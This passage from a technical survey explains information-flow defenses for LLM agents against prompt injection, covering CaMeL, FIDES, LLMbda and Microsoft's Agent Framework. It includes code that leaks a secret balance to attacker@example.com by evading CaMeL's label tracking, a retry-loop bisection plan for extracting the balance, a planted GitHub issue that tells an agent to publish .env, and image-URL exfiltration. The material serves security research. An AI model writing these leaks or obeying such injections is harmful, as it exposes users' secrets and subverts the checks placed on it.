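Nikolaou and colleagues first tried to reproduce CaMeL's own policies for AgentDojo. They could fully express the trust conditions of 22 of the 28 policies as rules that CaMeLoT can check in advance. Most of the others depended on facts that are known only at run time.

They then ran both systems on 97 AgentDojo tasks without any attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5. In 22 cases the plan failed to do what the user wanted under either system. The remaining 75 cases divided as follows:

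| | CaMeL allowed the plan | CaMeL blocked the plan |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeLoT allowed the plan | 42 | 9 |
| CaMeLoT blocked the plan | 7 | 17 |

The systems agreed in 59 cases. Since nobody was attacking, every blocked plan stopped legitimate work. CaMeLoT is meant to run before CaMeL, so a plan has to pass both. Together they would have completed 42 tasks, compared with 49 for CaMeL alone. But the test did not let the planner repair plans that broke a rule, and repairs might recover some of the seven tasks that only CaMeLoT blocked.

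To test rules about order and completion, Nikolaou and colleagues wrote one correct plan for the security-alert agent and seven faulty versions, each of which broke a different rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught only the one that used untrusted data. CaMeLoT also caught four faulty plans that a model had written, and the simplified CaMeL caught none of them. The rules were written for the faults in the test, so these results show what kinds of rule each system can express but not how often CaMeLoT would catch faults in practice. Checking in advance also doesn't explain all of the difference, because a runtime monitor that kept a history of calls could have enforced the rules about order.

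### False alarms, missing facts and the cost of rules

TACIT and CaMeLoT both reject some harmless programs. TACIT rejects any function that could use a permission on classified data, even if it would only print "done". CaMeLoT rejects some plans because of paths that could never occur or sources it cannot identify. In both systems, the model can rewrite a rejected program before any of it runs, so a false alarm usually causes only a short delay. On τ²-bench, between 0.3% and 7.9% of TACIT's programs needed another attempt, and the examples Odersky and colleagues give are ordinary coding errors. Nobody has measured how often TACIT's secrecy rule rejects harmless code.

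Both systems leave some decisions until the program runs. TACIT's compiler can confirm that a program has permission to use a folder, but the library has to check at run time that each requested file is inside it. The library checks website addresses and commands in the same way. CaMeLoT relies on CaMeL to check who may read a document, since the list of readers can change after the planner has written the program.

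The systems also differ in how much work one check covers. CaMeLoT checks the plan for the entire task, which the planner must write before seeing any results. A TACIT agent can write one short program, look at the unclassified results and then write another. This lets the agent adapt to what it finds, but if the compiler rejects its fifth program, the effects of the first four remain.

*Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) combines a check of the agent's plan before the run with a monitor that checks every call during it. Under one rule, an airline agent must confirm that a passenger has not yet flown before it cancels the booking. Soteria checks the plan against such rules with Dafny, a program that proves properties of code. The monitor is still necessary because some rules may remain unproved when the planner runs out of attempts, and because the model that carries out the plan may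 depart from it. CaMeL avoids the second problem because its interpreter runs the planner's program exactly as written.

In tests on 207 tasks, Soteria never broke a rule. This was nearly guaranteed because its monitor blocked any call that would have violated the rules used for scoring. Soteria also completed on average 1.7 times as many tasks as the best alternative, which is a more informative result. When the monitor blocked a call, the model could return to the plan and find another way to continue.

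All three systems require people to decide what the agent may do. TACIT's general library has about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the tool descriptions for the airline and retail tests took a few hundred lines each. TACIT's secrecy rule then applies to every program, including those written to leak data in ways nobody thought of. An administrator still has to choose which data to classify, and *Safe Scala*, an introduction by the software consultancy VirtusLab, warns that an agent becomes much less useful if too much is off limits.

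CaMeLoT's rules are short, but someone has to think of each one. If nobody writes a rule about approval, a plan that isolates computers without approval will pass. In TACIT, a developer could require approval before isolation by making the approval tool supply the permission that the isolation tool needs, which would also ensure that someone had actually approved the step. A requirement to close every ticket would be harder to express this way, because a permission can't force an agent to act.

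Language models can help write the rules. In CaMeLoT, a model can derive requirements from the user's request by choosing from ten fixed forms, which ordinary code then converts into temporal logic. All the resulting rules were valid in form, but the set of required actions was exactly right for only 85 of 97 requests. Because a valid rule can still require the wrong thing, He and colleagues have people check the model's draft rules against the written policy, clause by clause, and add any that are missing.

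## What the proofs guarantee, and on what assumptions

Tests can show that known attacks fail against an agent, but only a proof can show that every attack will fail. Such a proof needs an exact definition of what it means for data to have no effect. Several of the systems described so far have proofs, but the proofs use different definitions, and one definition can permit a leak that another rules out.

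### Noninterference

The standard definition is noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer introduced in 1982. A program is noninterfering if changing its secret inputs never changes anything an outside observer can see. Write x₁ ≈ x₂ if two inputs, or two outputs, look the same to the observer. Then a program P is noninterfering if, for all inputs,

x₁ ≈ x₂ ⇒ P(x₁) ≈ P(x₂)

The same formula covers integrity if two inputs count as alike when their trusted parts agree. It then means that untrusted data cannot change any trusted result. Wu and colleagues' guarantee for f-secure is of this kind.

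Noninterference is a property of pairs of runs. Suppose an outsider asks Alice's assistant whether she is free on Friday, and it answers "no". That answer reveals nothing if the assistant gives it to every outsider, but it reveals something private if the assistant checked her calendar and would have answered "yes" in a quieter week. The message is the same in both cases, so identifying the leak requires comparing what the assistant would send with different calendars.

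Noninterference is a property of pairs of runs, but a monitor observes only one run at a time. It can enforce a safety rule such as "never isolate a computer without requesting approval", because a single run can break that rule. No single run breaks noninterference by itself, so the monitor can only enforce something stricter, by stopping every run that might be part of a violating pair, including some harmless runs.

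Costa and colleagues considered noninterference too restrictive for FIDES because it would more or less forbid the agent from calling any tool that writes to a public place after calling one that might have read a secret. Dongol points out that useful agents also disclose private data on purpose. For example, an assistant that sends Alice's free hours to anyone who requests a meeting violates noninterference.

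### Explicit secrecy

For FIDES's labelled loop, Costa and colleagues instead proved explicit secrecy, which rules out direct flows of secret data but not implicit flows. Take one path that the agent can follow when the stored data is d₁, and let g be the combined effect of that path's steps on the data. The agent has explicit secrecy if, for every such path and every d₂,

d₁ ≈ d₂ ⇒ g(d₁) ≈ g(d₂)

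This looks like noninterference, but g stays fixed. The definition applies the same steps to d₂, even if the agent would have taken different steps with that data. A program with two branches shows what this leaves open:

```
if balance > 10000:
    post("yes")
else:
    post("no")
```

Here `post` writes to a public web page. On the first branch, g writes "yes" whatever the balance is, and on the other it always writes "no", so on either branch the page looks the same for d₁ and d₂. The program therefore has explicit secrecy, although anyone who reads the page learns whether the balance is above $10,000. `post(balance)` would fail the definition because its effect depends directly on the secret.

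FIDES would block many leaks of this kind anyway. A model's output inherits the label of the whole conversation, so if the planner has read the balance, even the word "yes" is labeled secret. But the permitted-flow policy checks the labels of a call's arguments, and text stored in a variable keeps its own label. After reading the balance, the planner could apparently still choose which of two stored public texts to post, which would reveal the same fact.

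Costa and colleagues regard explicit secrecy as a practical compromise, and note that web browsers and the smartphone privacy monitor TaintDroid have made the same compromise. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, respond that the property is weakest where a program can easily turn data into control flow, because leaks through control flow can be efficient. For example, twenty yes-or-no answers are enough to identify any whole-dollar balance up to about a million dollars. The FIDES proof also assumes that the model always gives the same reply to the same conversation, but commercial models generally do not.

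### A leak in CaMeL's interpreter

CaMeL tries to track implicit flows as well. Its interpreter keeps a program-counter label, which records what data influenced the program's route to the current step. Suppose a program contains these lines:

```
if balance > 10000:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich")
```

The condition reads a secret, so the program-counter label becomes secret and CaMeL refuses to send the email. Garby and colleagues found a way around this check that uses an assignment the program skips. Such a program looks roughly like this:

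```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich")
```

CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that the program takes. The two possible runs therefore go as follows:

| Line | Balance above $10,000 | Balance of $10,000 or less |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp = False` | runs, so `tmp` is False and secret | skipped, so `tmp` stays True and public |
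| `rich = False` | skipped, so `rich` stays True and public | runs, so `rich` is False and public |
| `send_email(...)` | runs, because `rich` is public | skipped |

In both runs, `rich` ends up holding the secret answer under a public label. Fenton described this trick in 1974, and Denning later rewrote it in the style of ordinary programming languages.

CaMeL's planner writes its program before it reads any untrusted data, so a line planted in an email could not normally make it write this leaking program. The leak matters if hostile text reaches the planner, as it did in the chain of CaMeL agents that Peters-Gill and colleagues attacked, or if the planner itself is hostile.

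Another flaw looks more dangerous when the planner is honest. Garby and colleagues found that inserting an untrusted value into a string template made CaMeL treat the value as trusted. Ordinary programs often use such templates, so an honest plan could accidentally let an attacker's text past a policy.

### The "no high upgrade" rule

A rule that Austin and Flanagan published in 2009 blocks the leak through `rich`. It forbids a program from changing a public variable while its program-counter label is secret. An assignment to a variable v may run only if

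label of the program counter ⊑ label of v

If the balance is above $10,000, the interpreter stops the program when it tries to change the public variable `tmp` after a secret test. If the balance is lower, the program finishes without sending the email, so the attacker gets no email in either case.

CaMeL instead lets the assignment run and raises the label of `tmp` to secret. That label is right in this run, but in the other run the program skips the assignment and `tmp` stays public, so the labels themselves depend on the secret. The rule prevents this, but it also stops some harmless programs. It would stop this program even if nothing used `tmp` afterwards.

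Garby and colleagues apply the rule in LLMbda, the small programming language they used to build the CaMeL-style agent described earlier. Variables in LLMbda never change, so the rule protects the conversation with the model instead. In their example, a program tells the model to remember that x is false. Then, only if a secret is true, the program tries to send a second message that sets x to true. The interpreter stops the program at that point, because the conversation would have stayed public without the second message.

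An observer who can see whether the program stopped still learns one bit. Most security definitions tolerate a leak of that size, but CaMeL's design lets a program repeat it. CaMeL runs its interpreter inside an ordinary Python loop, which has the planner try again if a program fails. The interpreter's labels don't extend to this loop. Each attempt therefore starts with clean labels, even though it depends on what happened in the last one. A hostile planner could use the loop like this:

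1. It writes a program that CaMeL will block only if the balance is above $500,000.
2. If CaMeL blocks the program, the next one tests for $750,000. Otherwise it tests for $250,000.
3. After about 20 attempts, the planner knows the balance to the dollar. It writes the number into a new program as an ordinary constant, which counts as public, and emails it out.

CaMeL censors the error messages that the planner receives, which makes this harder but comes with no formal guarantee. Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues built in LLMbda, avoids the problem by first testing and correcting its program on an invented bank account, where payments have no effect. The planner then writes a final version to run on the real account, so its failed attempts reveal nothing about the real data.

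### The LLMbda theorem

An LLMbda program can send messages to a model, run the model's reply as code, and open a side conversation that it later discards. Every value carries a label. The LLMbda theorem covers every program in the language, including code that a model writes during the run, whereas the FIDES proof covers one particular agent loop. Garby and colleagues proved the LLMbda theorem in Lean, a language that lets a computer check each step of a proof.

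A model's replies are random, so the theorem compares probabilities. Let ⟦C, e⟧ₘ be the probabilities of the different results when a program e starts with a conversation C, as seen by an observer who can read only data labelled m or lower. These probabilities may add up to less than 1. The missing part is the chance that the run never finishes, either because it loops forever or because a check stops it. The theorem states that, for every m,

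C₀ ~ₘ C₁ and e₀ ~ₘ e₁ ⇒ ⟦C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦C₁, e₁⟧ₘ

~ₘ means that two things look alike to the observer, and ⌣ means that two distributions are compatible. Distributions μ and ν are compatible if some distribution ω, with total probability at most 1, gives every result at least as much probability as μ and ν each do. In words, starting points that look alike to the observer give compatible distributions of results.

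Suppose the observer can see only whether a program returns "yes" or "no":

| | "yes" | "no" | Does not finish |
|---|---|---|---|
| μ (one value of the secret) | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| ν (another value) | 0.4 | 0.4 | 0.2 |
| ω | 0.5 | 0.4 | 0.1 |

These distributions are compatible because they could become identical if more runs finished. Suppose instead that every run finishes, and that "yes" has probability 0.6 with one secret and 0.4 with the other. Then ω would need to assign at least 0.6 to each of "yes" and "no", which adds up to at least 1.2, so the distributions are incompatible. The theorem guarantees that no LLMbda program behaves like this.

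Hidden data may therefore affect whether a run finishes, and this can shift the probabilities of the visible results to a limited extent. Let Δ(μ, ν) be half the sum of the differences between the probabilities of each result. Garby and colleagues prove that

Δ(μ, ν) ≤ ½ × (chance that μ does not finish + chance that ν does not finish)

In the table, Δ is 0.1 and the limit is 0.2. If every run finishes, the limit is zero and the two distributions must be identical, which is exact noninterference. But a program might always finish with one secret and never finish with another. Then Δ is 0.5, which equals the limit, and the observer learns one bit from whether the program stopped.

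The guarantee is weak for programs that often stop early, and it covers only one run at a time. If software outside the interpreter restarts a failed program and reacts to the failure, as in CaMeL's retry loop, the leak can grow again. A person who keeps retrying with slightly different requests could have the same effect.

For integrity, the observer sees only trusted results. Untrusted text cannot change those results, except by preventing the run from finishing. The theorem holds whatever a hostile reply contains. If the model writes code after reading untrusted text, that code runs with an untrusted program-counter label, so everything it computes is untrusted too.

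### How the proof works

To show that two distributions are compatible, Garby and colleagues have to find a suitable ω. They get it by defining a second, imaginary way to run a program. It works normally until a computation comes to depend on data that the observer cannot see. It then skips that computation and returns an empty value. They prove three facts about this skipping version:

- It gives each visible result at least as much probability as the real program does, because a computation that it skips cannot run forever or fail.
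- It gives the same probabilities for any two starting points that look alike to the observer, because it never uses the data that differs between them.
- Its probabilities add up to no more than 1.

If μ₀ and μ₁ are the real distributions for two such starting points, the skipping version gives a single ω for both, and

μ₀ ≤ ω and μ₁ ≤ ω

which is the definition of compatibility. Smith and Alpízar had used a similar argument in 2011 for simpler programs that flip coins. They deleted the secret parts from the text of the program, but that is impossible when a model writes some of the code during the run.

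Proofs about programming languages often describe a simplified version of the software that people run. LLMbda also includes a theorem about the interpreter that calls the model, showing that its results have the probabilities used in the main proof. This theorem assumes that each reply is a fresh random draw that depends only on the conversation so far. A model service that carried memories from one conversation to another would break this assumption and could let information bypass the labels.

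### Secrecy that survives endorsement

Agents sometimes need endorsement, the deliberate relabelling of untrusted data as trusted. For example, a program might extract Bob's address from Alice's meeting notes and endorse it to email him. Untrusted text can then affect trusted results, so the theorem's integrity guarantee no longer holds.

The guarantee for secrets does hold. Garby and colleagues split each label into an integrity half and a confidentiality half, and let endorsement lower only the integrity half. Endorsing Bob's address makes it trusted without changing who may read it. They then prove the theorem for every observer who can see both trusted and untrusted data, so only confidentiality limits what the observer sees. In this insulated version, secrets cannot reach public results, whatever untrusted text the attacker chooses and whatever the program endorses.

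Suppose an attacker has replaced the address in the notes with their own, and the program endorses it. A policy that requires a trusted recipient now allows the email. A policy on who may read the attached document would still block it, because the endorsement did not change the document's readers. The insulated theorem does not protect against a payment to a swapped bank account, because that harm does not involve secrecy.

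### Agents that are meant to disclose data

Dongol proposes another standard, relative security, for agents whose job includes revealing private data. It compares an agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor but never obeys instructions in untrusted text. The agent is relatively secure if an attacker can use it to tell apart two values of the user's data only when the attacker could also tell them apart using the reference agent. The plan sets the limit on what the agent may release, so nobody has to write a separate policy for that.

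Suppose Alice has told her assistant to send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An attacker's email doesn't request a meeting but orders the assistant to send the calendar. If the assistant obeys, it is still relatively secure, because a meeting request would have revealed the same calendar. The assistant is not relatively secure if the email also gets it to include a password-reset code, because no email could make the reference agent send that code.

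Dongol gives a computer-checked proof that a simple defence makes every plan relatively secure. When the agent first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently removes every tool that an injection could call. The theorem assumes that each injection triggers a single tool call, and that neither secrets nor the monitor's responses affect when the model obeys an injection. It also assumes that the attacker sees the content and order of messages but not their timing.

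The monitor has to act no later than that first read. If the agent reads a hostile email and then a secret, and the monitor removes its email tool only afterwards, an injected call can send the secret first. Acting this early means the agent can no longer reply to an email it has read, a restriction similar to that of the trusted-action policy in the basic labelled loop.

Relative security can be too weak. Suppose an agent tells anyone who guesses Alice's four-digit PIN whether the guess is right. An attacker can tell any two PINs apart by guessing one of them, so an injection that makes the agent send the whole PIN in one message counts as relatively secure, even though an attacker without the injection might need thousands of guesses. Dongol also defines a stricter version for such cases, in which the attacker's inputs to the reference agent must not depend on the secret. Both versions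 cover only leaks, not an injection that deletes Alice's files. A monitor that refuses every call also satisfies both versions, so developers have to test separately whether the agent can still do its work.

### From a theorem to a working agent

Developers want these proofs to support a simple claim, that untrusted data cannot cause a forbidden action. For an agent in use, the argument has five premises:

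1. **Labels.** All data that an outsider could have influenced arrives with an untrusted label.
2. **Tracking.** Everything derived from that data keeps the label.
3. **Checks.** Every consequential action has to pass a check of its labels against the policy.
4. **Tools.** Each tool does only what its description states.
5. **Planner.** The planner is honest, and chooses tool calls only to carry out the user's request.

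A computer-checked proof can show that the conclusion follows from premises like these. It doesn't show that the premises are true of a particular mailbox, browser or model, and each premise can be false.

Labels are often guesses. Costa and colleagues assume that only an email's sender and recipients may read it, but acknowledge that someone may have shared it more widely. Dongol points out that a calendar is not a trusted source if outsiders can send invitations to it, even though it may look like the user's own data. Costa and colleagues also mention that a system might relabel a document as trusted after a prompt-injection detector passes it, but warn that this could weaken the guarantee. The adaptive attacks by Nasr and colleagues, which beat such detectors most of the time, suggest that it would.

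Tracking can have gaps even in a carefully designed system, as the leaks in CaMeL show. Wu and colleagues proved their property for a formal model of f-secure, but according to Costa and colleagues, the practical system lets implicit flows influence its plans.

Labels can also disappear when data leaves the system that tracks them. The LLMbda theorem treats all data sources as part of the program, a limitation that Garby and colleagues list. A real agent might save an outsider's text to a shared drive and later read it back through a tool that labels every file there as trusted. Dongol's proofs assume that a new session clears everything the model has kept from untrusted text. That assumption is false if the agent keeps memory across sessions.

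Actions can bypass the check. For example, an agent may use a browser that the monitor does not control. Displaying a reply can also send data out. If the reply contains an image whose web address points to the attacker's server and includes a secret, the server receives the secret when the user's app automatically loads the image, without any tool call. By default, FIDES treats replies to the user as harmless and checks only tool calls, although Costa and colleagues explain how to check replies as well. Blocking an action can also leak information if the attacker can see the error message.

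The proofs also depend on accurate information about the tools. If a developer leaves a data source off the list of what a tool may read, FIDES may label the tool's result too permissively. Dongol excludes tools whose replies depend on the request, such as a search engine run by the attacker. The attacker would see the query, which might contain private data, and could write the answer to suit it. Costa and colleagues also assume that the descriptions telling the model how to use each tool are trustworthy. A malicious description could instruct the planner directly, and the planner's calls would still have trusted labels.

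The claim still holds if the planner is dishonest, but it is much less useful, because a policy that blocks only calls influenced by outsiders does not stop a planner from pursuing its own aims. Rules that apply to every call still constrain the planner. Garby and colleagues argue that if an LLMbda program endorses nothing, even a fully compromised model can do only what the checks in the tools permit. Their argument requires tracking that has no gaps, because a hostile planner can deliberately write programs like the one with `tmp` and `rich`.

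### What lies outside the theorems

Even if every assumption holds, an attacker may learn something from how long an agent takes. Costa and colleagues exclude timing and the size of network packets from their guarantee, and LLMbda's definition of a result does not include time. Dongol counts steps but does not measure elapsed time, and finds that the step count alone can expose a leak.

Suppose Alice approves the exact reply "Friday" to an email, and the monitor allows one message with that text. The email contains an injected instruction to send the day of her medical appointment. If the appointment is on Tuesday, the monitor blocks the injected message, and Alice's reply goes out as planned. If it is on Friday, the injected message matches the approved text and goes out one step early, and the monitor then blocks the planned reply as a second message. The attacker receives one "Friday"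 message either way, but its early arrival would reveal that the appointment is on Friday.

The theorems also do not guarantee that an answer is correct. In one of AgentDojo's banking tasks, the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a false request. This was the only attack that succeeded against Randori, whose planner had endorsed the file's contents. Garby and colleagues consider information-flow control unable to prevent such attacks. Labels can stop them only by blocking every payment based on the file, including genuine ones.

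Misleading text can also reach people without breaking any policy. With FIDES's policy checks switched on, AgentDojo's automatic scoring still counted three successful injections, all in chat tasks. Costa and colleagues inspected these by hand and reduced the count to zero. Across their tests, the cases they discounted included chat messages that the policies allowed because they contained no web links, and attacks that changed some text without altering the agent's steps or leaking secrets. A colleague who believes a false chat message may do what the attacker wanted, and no monitor will check that person's actions.

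## Policies, exceptions and human approval

The proofs assume that all data arrives with the right labels and that the policy forbids the right actions. In a working agent, people have to supply the labels and write the policy. They also have to decide when to allow exceptions, because an agent that can never act on text from outsiders is of little use for handling email.

### Where labels come from

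Software can label data only by the information it has about the source. Costa and colleagues wrap each tool in a function that labels the tool's results before the agent receives them. For an email, the function can list the sender and recipients as the permitted readers. To set the integrity label, it can use DMARC, a system that lets mail servers check whether a message came from the domain in its sender address. The function can label a whole result or each field separately, so an email might have a trusted date and an untrusted body.

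Authentication confirms where a message came from, but not whether the sender deserves trust. In one AgentDojo task reproduced by Kolluri and colleagues, the user wants a password reset link for a service called TechServices. The agent's search finds two emails, one from support@techservices.com and one from tech-services-password@aol.com. Both could pass a DMARC check, and a rule that trusts every authenticated sender would trust both, so someone has to decide which senders to trust.

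Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a simpler rule for GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools. The server labels files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. Once an agent has read both, its conversation counts as untrusted and private, and the policy stops the agent from posting to a public page. This blocks attacks like GitLost. But if an employee copies a customer's bug report into a private repository, the server labels the customer's text as trusted.

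If nobody has labelled a tool, the software can guess the labels from the tool's description. Microsoft suggests treating results as untrusted if the tool reaches the open internet, and as private if it requires a login. The guess depends on the accuracy of the description, which the tool's own developers usually write.

### Who writes the policies

In Microsoft's prototype, a tool's developers can publish a policy along with the tool. The policy is in Rego, a language for access rules, and returns "allow", "deny" or "ask". For tools without one, the company suggests some general rules:

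- Always allow tools that only read data within a closed system.
- Allow tools that read from the outside world only if everything sent to them is public.
- Ask the user before running a tool whose description marks it as destructive.

Tool policies are hard to write because the developers who understand a tool don't know what each company considers secret, and the company, which does know, may use hundreds of tools. Tallam and Miller warn that CaMeL's separate policy for each tool leads to "policy sprawl", in which teams write duplicate or inconsistent rules that nobody audits as a whole. They recommend writing policies in a language such as Rego, with shared rules like "share only within the company's domain". Shared rules are easier to check, though a mistake in one affects every tool that uses it.

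### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

On 20 May 2026, Microsoft released a version of FIDES in Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes the release as experimental, and it is available only for Python. FIDES gives each piece of content an integrity label (trusted or untrusted) and a confidentiality label (public, private or user identity). User identity is the strictest confidentiality label and covers personal data and passwords.

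The launch post follows an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. An attacker posts a report with a planted instruction to read a file called `.env`, which often contains passwords, and publish its contents:

1. The agent reads the report, which the tool labels as untrusted and public.
2. The model obeys the instruction and opens `.env`. The software allows this but labels the contents private, so the conversation is now both untrusted and private.
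3. The model tries to post the contents as a comment. The comment tool accepts only public data, so the software stops the call and asks the user.
4. If the instruction had been to change a file, the software would also have stopped that call, because the file-writing tool refuses to run in an untrusted conversation.

In this example, only the confidentiality rule stops the comment. Unless the developer also adds an integrity rule, a planted instruction could apparently make the agent post a false comment in the project's name, as long as the comment contains only public information.

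Microsoft's documentation lists these defaults:

| Situation | Default behaviour |
|---|---|
| A tool returns untrusted text | The planner sees only a variable name |
| The planner queries the quarantined model | It gets placeholder text until the developer supplies a model |
| A call breaks the policy | The software blocks it without asking the user |
| A tool returns data without a label | The data counts as untrusted and public |
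| The software blocks a call | It records the event in an audit log |

The launch post contradicts one of these defaults. It warns that a tool the developer forgets to label counts as trusted and public, so an unlabeled web-search tool would let injections through. The documentation's default of untrusted and public is safer, and Microsoft describes it as failing closed, but it fails closed only for integrity. If a developer forgets to label a tool that reads payroll files, the salaries count as public under either description, and the confidentiality rule would let the agent post them.

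Developers can track labels without blocking anything, so they can see what a policy would stop before they turn it on. Under Microsoft's general safety guidance, application developers remain responsible for validating inputs, securing data flows and configuring tools appropriately.

### Other problems for companies

Tallam and Miller see several obstacles to using CaMeL in a company, including policy sprawl, its trust in the user's first message and its failure to check the final answer. They propose screening the first message and the final answer for suspicious text, but an attacker who adapts can probably get past such filters.

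Their proposal for uploaded files fits better with labels. Every value taken from an uploaded file would carry a tag such as `from_user_upload`, and a policy could keep tagged values out of irreversible actions, such as sending external email, unless someone grants an exception.

They also describe leaks through the number of times a program repeats a step:

```
for i in range(secret):
    fetch("ping")
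```

Each request contains only the word "ping", but anyone who can read the website's access logs can count the requests and learn the secret number. An interpreter could cap the number of repetitions, combine the requests into one, or restrict tool calls inside any loop whose length depends on a secret.

Splitting the work between a planner and a quarantined model also makes the system slower and more expensive. Tallam and Miller assume that GPT-4 takes one to two seconds to respond, and estimate that processing ten emails could take more than ten seconds. Those figures are old, but the split still requires extra model calls. Tallam and Miller suggest reusing plans for common requests, reading structured data with ordinary code, and giving the quarantined model many items in one prompt. Combining items weakens security, because a hostile item can then affect the model's answers about the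 others.

### Why agents need exceptions

Useful agents need endorsement, which relabels untrusted data as trusted, and declassification, which relabels secret data as releasable. Without them, a policy could stop Alice's assistant from using the address in the meeting notes or sending Bob the date of the next payday, even when nobody is attacking.

Garby and colleagues measured how much their banking agent, Randori, depends on endorsement. They ran 16 AgentDojo tasks three times each. Using Qwen3.7-plus, the agent completed 36 of the 48 runs with endorsement and 30 without it. Using MiMo-v2.5, it completed 31 and 26. Three of the tasks require the agent to read a file and act on its contents, which is impossible if those contents must stay untrusted.

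Making endorsement available reduced security only slightly in these tests. With it, attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs across three models, and both involved the swapped payment file described earlier.

An attacker who gets a model to write code might include an endorsement in it. In LLMbda, code built from untrusted data runs with an untrusted program-counter label, and an endorsement cannot raise a value's integrity above that of the code that performs it. The attacker's endorsement therefore has no effect unless an earlier endorsement made the attacker's text trusted.

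To prevent such chains, Garby and colleagues describe a stricter version that marks every endorsed value and stops the program if it tries to endorse a marked value again. This version also removes the ability to endorse from code that models write during the run.

### Answers with a fixed set of options

An exception is easier to justify if the attacker can influence only a small choice. FIDES records this by adding a type to each label. The types form an order based on how much information they can carry:

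yes/no ⊑ a choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text

Constrained decoding can enforce the output's type by preventing the model from producing anything outside the permitted format. A policy can then accept an untrusted yes-or-no answer where it would reject untrusted free text.

Costa and colleagues illustrate this with a user who asks an agent to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, add the meeting to the calendar:

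1. The agent fetches the emails, and the software stores their text in a variable.
2. The planner has the quarantined model check for a meeting request, and allows only a yes-or-no answer.
3. The planner reads the answer. Its conversation now contains untrusted data, but only one bit of it.
4. If the answer is "yes", the planner has the quarantined model extract the meeting's details into a second variable.
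5. The planner creates the event from that variable without reading it.

Under the basic trusted-action policy, the software would block step 5. A looser policy that accepts yes-or-no answers can allow it. The attacker can still choose the meeting's date and guests, so the policy has to control those separately. Costa and colleagues did not test constrained decoding, because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need it.

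In LLMbda, a program makes the exception itself, with a command called `endorse`. Garby and colleagues give the example of an agent that sorts an email into a category and uses the category as the subject of its reply. The email tool requires a trusted subject, so the program has to endorse the category. A safer version of the command accepts only values from a fixed list. In simplified form, it works like this:

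```
copy = endorse(answer)
if copy in ["billing", "support", "sales", "other"]:
    return copy
else:
    return answer
```

If the quarantined model returns a planted sentence instead of a category, the program passes on the original, untrusted answer, and the email tool rejects it. The program must endorse the copy before checking the list. If it checked the untrusted answer first, the code inside the `if` would run with an untrusted program-counter label, and the endorsement would have no effect.

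### Counting the bits

An answer chosen from n options carries at most log₂ n bits. If the quarantined model sorts one email into four classes, the attacker can influence at most

log₂ 4 = 2 bits

Fifty such emails carry at most

50 × 2 = 100 bits

because there are 4⁵⁰ possible sets of answers, or about 1.3 × 10³⁰. At seven bits per character, 100 bits can encode 14 characters of plain text, which is long enough for many passwords.

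How much of this an attacker controls depends on how the agent sorts the emails. If each email goes to a separate quarantined call, an attacker who wrote one email can influence only two bits. If a single call sorts all fifty, one hostile email might change every answer. The agent can also reduce the total by keeping only the number of emails in each class, which leaves 23,426 possible results, or about 14.5 bits.

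Even 100 bits of category names are unlikely to hijack a planner, because it receives only a list of words like "billing" and "support". The greater risk is that they leak secrets. Suppose the quarantined model can also read a private file, and the agent sends a different automatic reply for each category. An attacker who wrote all fifty emails could make the model encode a password in its choice of categories, then read the password from the replies.

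The number of bits in an answer does not measure how much harm it can do. A single yes-or-no answer can decide whether an agent pays an invoice or deletes a folder. One of the lists that Costa and colleagues suggest has the quarantined model choose among scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding an email. That choice carries only about 1.6 bits, but an attacker who can make the model choose "forward" may cause a leak if nothing else restricts the recipient.

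A ten-digit account number carries about 33 bits, a third as much as the fifty sorted emails, but it is enough to redirect a payment. Developers therefore need to consider how much harm the worst option could do, as well as how many options there are.

Garby and colleagues accept that their fixed-list version would reject the account numbers and amounts their banking agent most needs to endorse. They argue that the user's request justifies endorsing these values. If Alice asks the agent to pay the bill in a certain file, she has chosen to trust that file. They leave a formal proof of the log₂ n limit to future work.

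### Robust declassification

Robust declassification means that an attacker cannot cause or influence the release of secret data. In an agent with labels, it usually takes the form of a rule that only a trusted conversation may declassify anything. Microsoft gives an example policy for posting a message to a group chat:

1. If the conversation is trusted, allow the message.
2. If everyone in the chat may already read the text, allow it.
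3. Otherwise, ask the user and list the people who would gain access.

A prompt injection makes the conversation untrusted, so it can't use the exception in step 1. But that exception does nothing about the model's own mistakes. In another of Microsoft's examples, Alex asks an agent to answer some email. Priya has sent Alex the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see them yet, has asked about them. Once the agent has read both emails, the permitted readers of its reply are

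{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}

so a rule based only on readers stops the agent from sending the reply to Marco. If an email policy copied the group-chat rule, the result would depend on the integrity labels too. If the software labelled colleagues' emails as trusted, step 1 would allow the reply, and Marco would get the figures.

A mistaken endorsement can also defeat robust declassification. If Alice endorses an email that contains a planted instruction, the conversation stays trusted, and step 1 would let the agent post her private files. LLMbda avoids this because its endorsements never make secret data releasable, as its insulated theorem shows.

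### Approving data or approving actions

A person who approves a blocked tool call makes an exception to the policy for that call. Kolluri and colleagues designed Prudentia, an agent built on FIDES, to ask for fewer of these exceptions, and presented it at the machine-learning conference ICLR in 2026.

Prudentia's planner has access to the policy for each tool and the label of its own conversation. Before it opens a variable that contains untrusted text, it has to state why it needs the text and which calls it plans to make afterwards. It can then open the variable and let the conversation become untrusted, or ask the user to endorse the text and keep the conversation trusted.

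Suppose an email contains a to-do list with ten items, each requiring a consequential action. If the planner reads the email without endorsement, the user has to approve ten separate calls, whereas endorsing the email takes only one approval. But that endorsement would also cover a planted eleventh item, which the user would have a chance to notice when approving each action separately.

Prudentia has no similar blanket exception for secrets. Kolluri and colleagues argue that whether to release private data depends too much on the situation, so the user has to approve each call.

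They propose two measures of an agent's autonomy. Let v be the number of times the agent would have to ask a person during a task:

- **HITL load** is the sum of v over all the tasks the agent completes. HITL stands for "human in the loop".
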